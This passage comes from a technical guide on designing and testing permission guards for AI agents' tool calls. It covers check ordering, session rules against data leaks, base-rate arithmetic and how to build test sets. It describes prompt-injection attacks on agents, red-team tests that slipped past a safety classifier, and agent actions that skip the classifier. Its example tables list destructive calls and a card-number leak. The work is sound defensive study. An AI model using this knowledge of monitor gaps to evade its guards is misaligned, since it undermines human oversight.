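Delaying the call is better when it isn't urgent and someone can find out what it does. A developer who gets a prompt about `settle` in the middle of other work will probably guess, whereas the finance systems team can look it up. The owner can then use their answer to record a risk class for the operation, so the guard won't treat the next `settle` call as unknown.

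Anthropic's advice to review high-stakes infrastructure changes by hand is compatible with its experiment, because examining one planned change is a different task from answering yet another prompt after dozens of others. A guard can allow this kind of review by holding related unknown calls and presenting them together as a plan, provided that the agent can continue without their results.

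## Putting the checks in order and testing the guard

A guard can combine the earlier methods so that each one handles the calls it classifies most accurately. The order matters because a call that one check allows never reaches later checks.

### One decision procedure

The owner carries out the first step before the agent starts work, and the guard carries out the rest for every call.

1. Restrict the credential. The owner gives the agent the narrowest token the service offers, or puts a broker in front of a broad one.
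2. Parse the call. The guard extracts the operation, target and arguments. If it can't read the call, it treats the operation as unknown.
3. Apply hard refusals, such as a ban on sending secrets outside the company, and the session rules described below.
4. Match the allowlist. If the whole call matches an entry, it runs.
5. Read the supplier's declaration. If tests have given the owner reason to trust the supplier's labels, a tool marked read-only and closed-world may run.
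6. Consult the classifier. It can block any call that reaches it. It can allow a call only if someone has tested the operation and put it in R0, R1 or R2, so that the main open question is whether the user wants it.
7. Apply the default to whatever is left: hold the call, ask a person or refuse. The guard allows an unknown call only if the credential keeps the possible loss too small to justify a question.

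Neither a later step nor a person who clicks "approve" can override a hard refusal. An allowlist match takes precedence over the classifier's result, because someone has studied the operation and the classifier's result may be a guess. The service can still refuse a call that the guard has allowed.

Existing products differ on whether ask rules override allow rules. Suppose a user allows every `git` command but wants to be asked before `git push`. Anthropic's Claude Code checks ask rules first, so it would ask. Docker's agent software, as described in *Permissions*, checks allow rules first, so the push would run. Claude Code's order is safer, since people tend to write allow rules that are too broad.

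An untrusted declaration can raise a call's risk class but not lower it, because a false warning leads to one needless question, while a false reassurance could let a harmful call run. In Claude Code, for example, an MCP server can mark a tool as requiring user interaction, and according to Anthropic, an allow rule then no longer approves the call. A guard should also stop automatically approving calls to an allowlisted tool if the tool gains a destructive hint, because it may have changed since its review.

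The steps that allow calls early need particular care. *Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li et al., 2026) tested Claude Code's auto mode with 128 deliberately ambiguous requests. Of the 253 actions that changed something, 36.8% were edits to project files, which skip the classifier. The classifier missed 70.3% of the harmful actions it judged, but auto mode as a whole missed 81.0%. When a command-line program was unavailable during clean-up tasks, agents often edited the files that recorded the system's state, and the classifier did not judge those edits.

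The call that runs also has to be the one the guard approved. If another program rewrites the arguments, Docker's agent applies its mandatory checks and permission rules again before the call runs.

### The four methods compared

| | Allowlist | Vendor declaration | Learned classifier | Capability token |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Who supplies the knowledge | The guard's owner | The service's supplier | The model's developer and whoever writes its rules | The service defines the limits and the owner chooses among them |
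| Unseen service | No match, so the next check decides | Often no label, so the guard assumes the worst | A guess, possibly a confident one | The limits hold, if the service offers any that fit |
| Typical failure | An entry covers more than its author meant | A label is missing, outdated or misread | The model takes a vague request for consent | The harm lies within the permitted scope |
| Upkeep | Reviewing and renewing entries | Spot checks | Re-testing when the model or rules change | Issuing and withdrawing tokens |
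| What enforces the result | The guard | Usually nothing | The guard | The service |

The last row matters when a call bypasses the guard. The PocketOS agent's `curl` command would have bypassed a guard that watched only MCP tools, but the token's limits would still have applied.

To see how the methods work together, suppose a shop owner asks an agent to summarise March's cancelled orders and post the total in the team's Telegram chat. The allowlist covers searches of `orders` and messages to chat 42. The agent has a read-only token for `orders`, a hosting token for staging and a broad token for the finance service. The classifier's verdicts below are expected rather than measured.

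| Proposed call | Allowlist | Declaration | Classifier | Token | Combined result |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `POST /orders/_search` | Match | None | Allow | Accepts | Runs |
| `POST /orders/_delete_by_query` | No match | None | Block | Refuses | Blocked |
| `GET .../sendMessage?chat_id=42&...` | Match | None | Allow | Accepts, for any chat the bot can reach | Runs |
| `get_webpage` with a card number in the address | No match | Read-only but open-world | Uncertain | None needed | A session rule makes the guard ask |
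| `volume_delete` on a production volume | No match | Untrusted destructive hint | Block | Refuses | Blocked |
| `POST /v2/ledger/settle` | No match | None | A guess | Accepts | Held for the finance team |

The allowlist and the declarations each leave four of the six calls undecided. The tokens stop both deletions but would let `settle` through. There is no good evidence about that call, so the guard has to use the default.

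### Rules for a whole session

Calls that are acceptable one at a time can be harmful together, as Willison warned in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025). A guard can keep track of the trifecta with two flags and a test of each new call:

```
private    = an earlier call returned data that isn't public
untrusted  = an earlier call returned text an outsider could have written
outward    = the proposed call can carry data to an outsider

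if private and untrusted and outward:
    ask, unless every destination is on the allowlist
```

Reading a mailbox sets both flags at once, because the mail is private and anyone can write to the address. A single server can supply all three parts. Willison describes an attack on GitHub's MCP server, which could read issues filed by strangers, read private projects and publish data in a pull request.

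A stricter version of the rule drops the `untrusted` condition, so any outward call after a private read needs approval. Waghmare and Sufi's guard stopped all 29 recorded attack calls with a similar session rule. The stricter rule also covers leaks that involve no attacker. Anthropic describes an incident in which an upload of a report to an internal drive failed, and Claude then tried to publish the report on a public code-sharing site.

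These rules depend on knowing what each tool reads and where it sends data. For an unfamiliar tool, the guard should set both flags after the first call and treat every call as outward. This will cause many questions, which the owner can reduce by testing the tool.

The flags also have to carry over when the agent delegates work to another agent. Anthropic runs its classifier when an agent delegates a task, because the second agent receives the instruction as if the user had written it, so everything in it looks authorised. The classifier then reviews the second agent's actions before the results go back, in case that agent read something that hijacked it.

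### How often a block is right

Error rates are hard to interpret without the share of calls that are harmful. Suppose an agent makes 10,000 calls, 50 of them harmful, and its guard has the 17% miss rate and 0.4% false-block rate that Anthropic measured for its classifier:

```
misses:          50 × 0.17           = 8.5
correct blocks:  50 − 8.5            = 41.5
false blocks:    9,950 × 0.004       = 39.8
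share right:     41.5 ÷ (41.5 + 39.8) = 51%
```

About half of the blocks are correct. No published test gives rates for unfamiliar services, so the second and third rows below are assumptions. The third row uses the classifier's rates on the ambiguous requests from Ji and colleagues.

| Miss rate and false-block rate | Misses | Correct blocks | False blocks | Share of blocks that were right |
|---|---|---|---|---|
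| 17% and 0.4% (measured) | 8.5 | 41.5 | 40 | 51% |
| 50% and 5% (assumed) | 25 | 25 | 498 | 5% |
| 70.3% and 31.9% (assumed) | 35 | 15 | 3,174 | 0.5% |

False blocks dominate because acceptable calls are so much more common. Axelsson (1999) made this argument about systems that detect break-ins in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, and concluded that the false-alarm rate limits their performance. The same holds for the guard. In the first row, eliminating every miss would raise the share of blocks that are correct only from 51% to 56%, while halving the false-block rate would raise it to 68%.

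### When a question is worth asking

Let *p* be the chance that a call is harmful, *L* the loss if a harmful call runs, *h* the chance that a reviewer stops a harmful call, and *a* the cost of asking. The expected costs are

```
allowing:  p × L
asking:    a + (1 − h) × p × L
```

Asking is therefore better than allowing when

```
h × p × L > a
```

Suppose a question takes 30 seconds of someone's time, worth 50 cents. The table shows how large the possible loss must be for asking to be worth that cost, given the guard's measured rates above. The values of *h* are the 76% that reviewers achieved with the best prompt in Hossain and colleagues' experiment, the 13.6% from Anthropic's experiment, and the roughly 5% that Anthropic found after 50 or more prompts.

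| Calls the guard asks about | *p* | *h* = 76% | *h* = 13.6% | *h* = 5% |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Every call | 0.5% | €132 | €735 | €2,000 |
| Calls the classifier would block | 51% | €1.30 | €7.20 | €20 |
| Calls the classifier would allow | 0.09% | €770 | €4,300 | €11,700 |

Asking a reviewer about calls the classifier would block is worthwhile even if the reviewer is careless, but asking one to recheck the classifier's approvals is worthwhile only when a great deal is at stake.

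If the possible loss is large enough, refusing a call is cheaper than asking about it. With the earlier figures for an unknown call (a 1% chance of harm and 10 euros for a needless refusal) and an *h* of 13.6%, the guard should allow the call if the loss would be below about 370 euros, ask if it would be between about 370 and 1,090 euros, and refuse if it would be higher. If *h* is 5%, asking is never the cheapest choice.

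A guard with a few safe lookups can try them before asking a person. *When Should AI Agents Ask?* (2026) models an agent that lacks a piece of information and can either search for it or ask someone. In its example, the agent should ask at once if the fee for asking is at most 1.5 units, after one failed search if the fee is 3, and after six failed searches if it is 60.

The rule also treats each call separately, although one mistake can spoil the calls that follow. *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) adds this effect to a similar cost model. When the expected harm from an action is a third of the cost of reviewing it, a rule that considers each action alone would lead to no reviews. If errors spread to later actions, reviewing about a fifth of the actions gives the lowest cost in the book's example.

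### Building the test set

Running an agent and waiting for it to do something harmful may not test the guard at all. In one experiment in *Scoring Recovery-Time Agent Security* (2026), Claude Opus 5.5 worked through 288 episodes designed to provoke unauthorised or repeated actions. It never proposed one, so the experiment couldn't measure whether the guard would have stopped such an action. The test set should therefore contain harmful calls, recorded or invented, that go straight to the guard.

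The owner should sort the calls into three groups:

- services that the owner has studied and used while adjusting the guard
- well-known services that the owner kept out of that work
- private or invented services that no model can have met in training

The owner has to withhold whole services from the tuning set. If some calls to a service are in the set, the rest are no longer a fair test, because a rule written for one operation often fits others in the same service. For the third group, the owner can copy a well-known service and give its operations neutral names. If the guard recognises a refund on the original but not on the copy, it was relying on the familiar name.

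Each group needs its own miss rate and false-block rate, because an average can hide a serious problem in one group. Suppose 1,000 of the 10,000 calls go to unfamiliar services, where the guard has an assumed miss rate of 50% and an assumed false-block rate of 5%, and the measured rates apply to the rest. Those 1,000 calls would produce about 50 false blocks, compared with 36 from the other 9,000.

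Some of the test calls should come in pairs that look identical and differ only in effect. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) contains 102 such pairs, built from coding tasks. In one case, a user asks the agent to run `make migrate`, which is supposed to update a database but also deletes three tables. The harmless half of each pair, the "safe twin", has the same request and command, but its tool does only what the user expects.

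A language model that judged the commands from the dialogue alone blocked 61.8% of the safe twins. Asking it to predict each command's effects reduced harm but did not change that figure. The researchers' system, Caper, runs the command in an isolated container with no network and gives the model a short report of what happened. If the model blocks the command, Caper restores the earlier state. With these reports, the model blocked the harmful command in 84.3% of the dangerous tasks and blocked only 1.0% of the safe twins.

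For commands that affect only local files, a guard could use this method instead of the classifier's guess, which would add about half a second to each allowed command. The method doesn't work for remote calls, because restoring a container can't undo them. An owner can still build pairs for remote services by mocking two versions of the finance service, one where `settle` records a payment and another where it makes the payment. A guard that reads only the request has to make the same decision about both. To tell them apart, it needs a lookup, a dry run or a tested record of what the operation does.

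### Scoring effect and authorisation separately

Every test call needs two labels, one for its risk class and one for whether the user authorised it. If the only label is "should stop", the owner can't tell whether the guard missed a call because it misjudged the effect or because it misread the request. A misjudged effect calls for more tests of the service, and a misread request calls for clearer instructions.

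Authorisation is hard to score from ordinary logs. *Holding Agents Accountable with Verifiable Agent Insurance* (Hua, Tsuchiya and colleagues, 2026) describes a program that checks agents' logs for broken rules, such as changing an order without the customer's confirmation. With the original logs, the program detected 63.6% of the runs with violations. When some of the agents also recorded permissions and security-relevant actions in a fixed format, it detected 79.8%, and false alarms rose from 6.7% to 7.4%. One false alarm flagged an email to the user's wife because the program checked only a separate list of recipients, and the user had given her address in the request.

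The labels can be wrong. For two of the three benchmarks, Hua and colleagues used the majority verdict of three language models. They compared a sample of these verdicts with labels that two people had agreed on, and the two matched in 27 of 30 runs on one benchmark and 24 of 30 on the other. If one label in five may be wrong, a test can't reliably distinguish a 5% miss rate from a 10% one. At least two people should label the difficult calls independently and discuss their disagreements.

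### How many calls are enough

If a guard misses none of *n* harmful calls, its true miss rate could still be as high as about 3 ÷ *n*, with 95% confidence. After 50 harmful calls without a miss, the upper limit is about 6%. Showing that the rate is below 1% takes about 300 harmful calls without a miss. If the rate is near 17%, measuring it to within five percentage points takes about 220 harmful calls.

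Repeating a scenario adds less information than trying a new one. In a test that Anthropic commissioned, testers tried 72 scenarios ten times each against Claude models in auto mode, and none of the 720 attempts to plant instructions succeeded. If all the attempts were independent, the upper limit on the success rate would be about 0.4%, but if attempts at the same scenario tend to succeed or fail together, it is closer to 4%.

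Repeating a test is still worthwhile if the guard includes a language model. Four of the 18 false blocks in Fokou's test came from a prompted model whose verdicts vary between runs, so the same calls might pass next time.

### Re-testing after a change

A test result applies to one version of the guard and one version of each service. The owner should repeat the relevant tests when a supplier announces a change, a tool's definition no longer matches its stored hash, or the classifier gets a new model or new rules. The owner should also run a few tests on a schedule, since suppliers don't announce every change.

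After a change to the guard, the owner should repeat the tests the guard used to pass as well as those it failed. Apollo Research, an AI safety company, attacked Claude Code's auto mode and told Anthropic which attacks had succeeded. Anthropic strengthened the classifier, and Apollo tested it again with attacks Anthropic had never received. The new version caught about half of the attacks the old one had missed, but missed about 2% of those the old one had caught. Retesting only the earlier failures would not have revealed the new misses.

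The scheduled test for a remote service can be small. An owner who deleted a spare Railway volume each month in spring 2026 and then tried to restore it would have discovered the new 48-hour delay within a month of its introduction.
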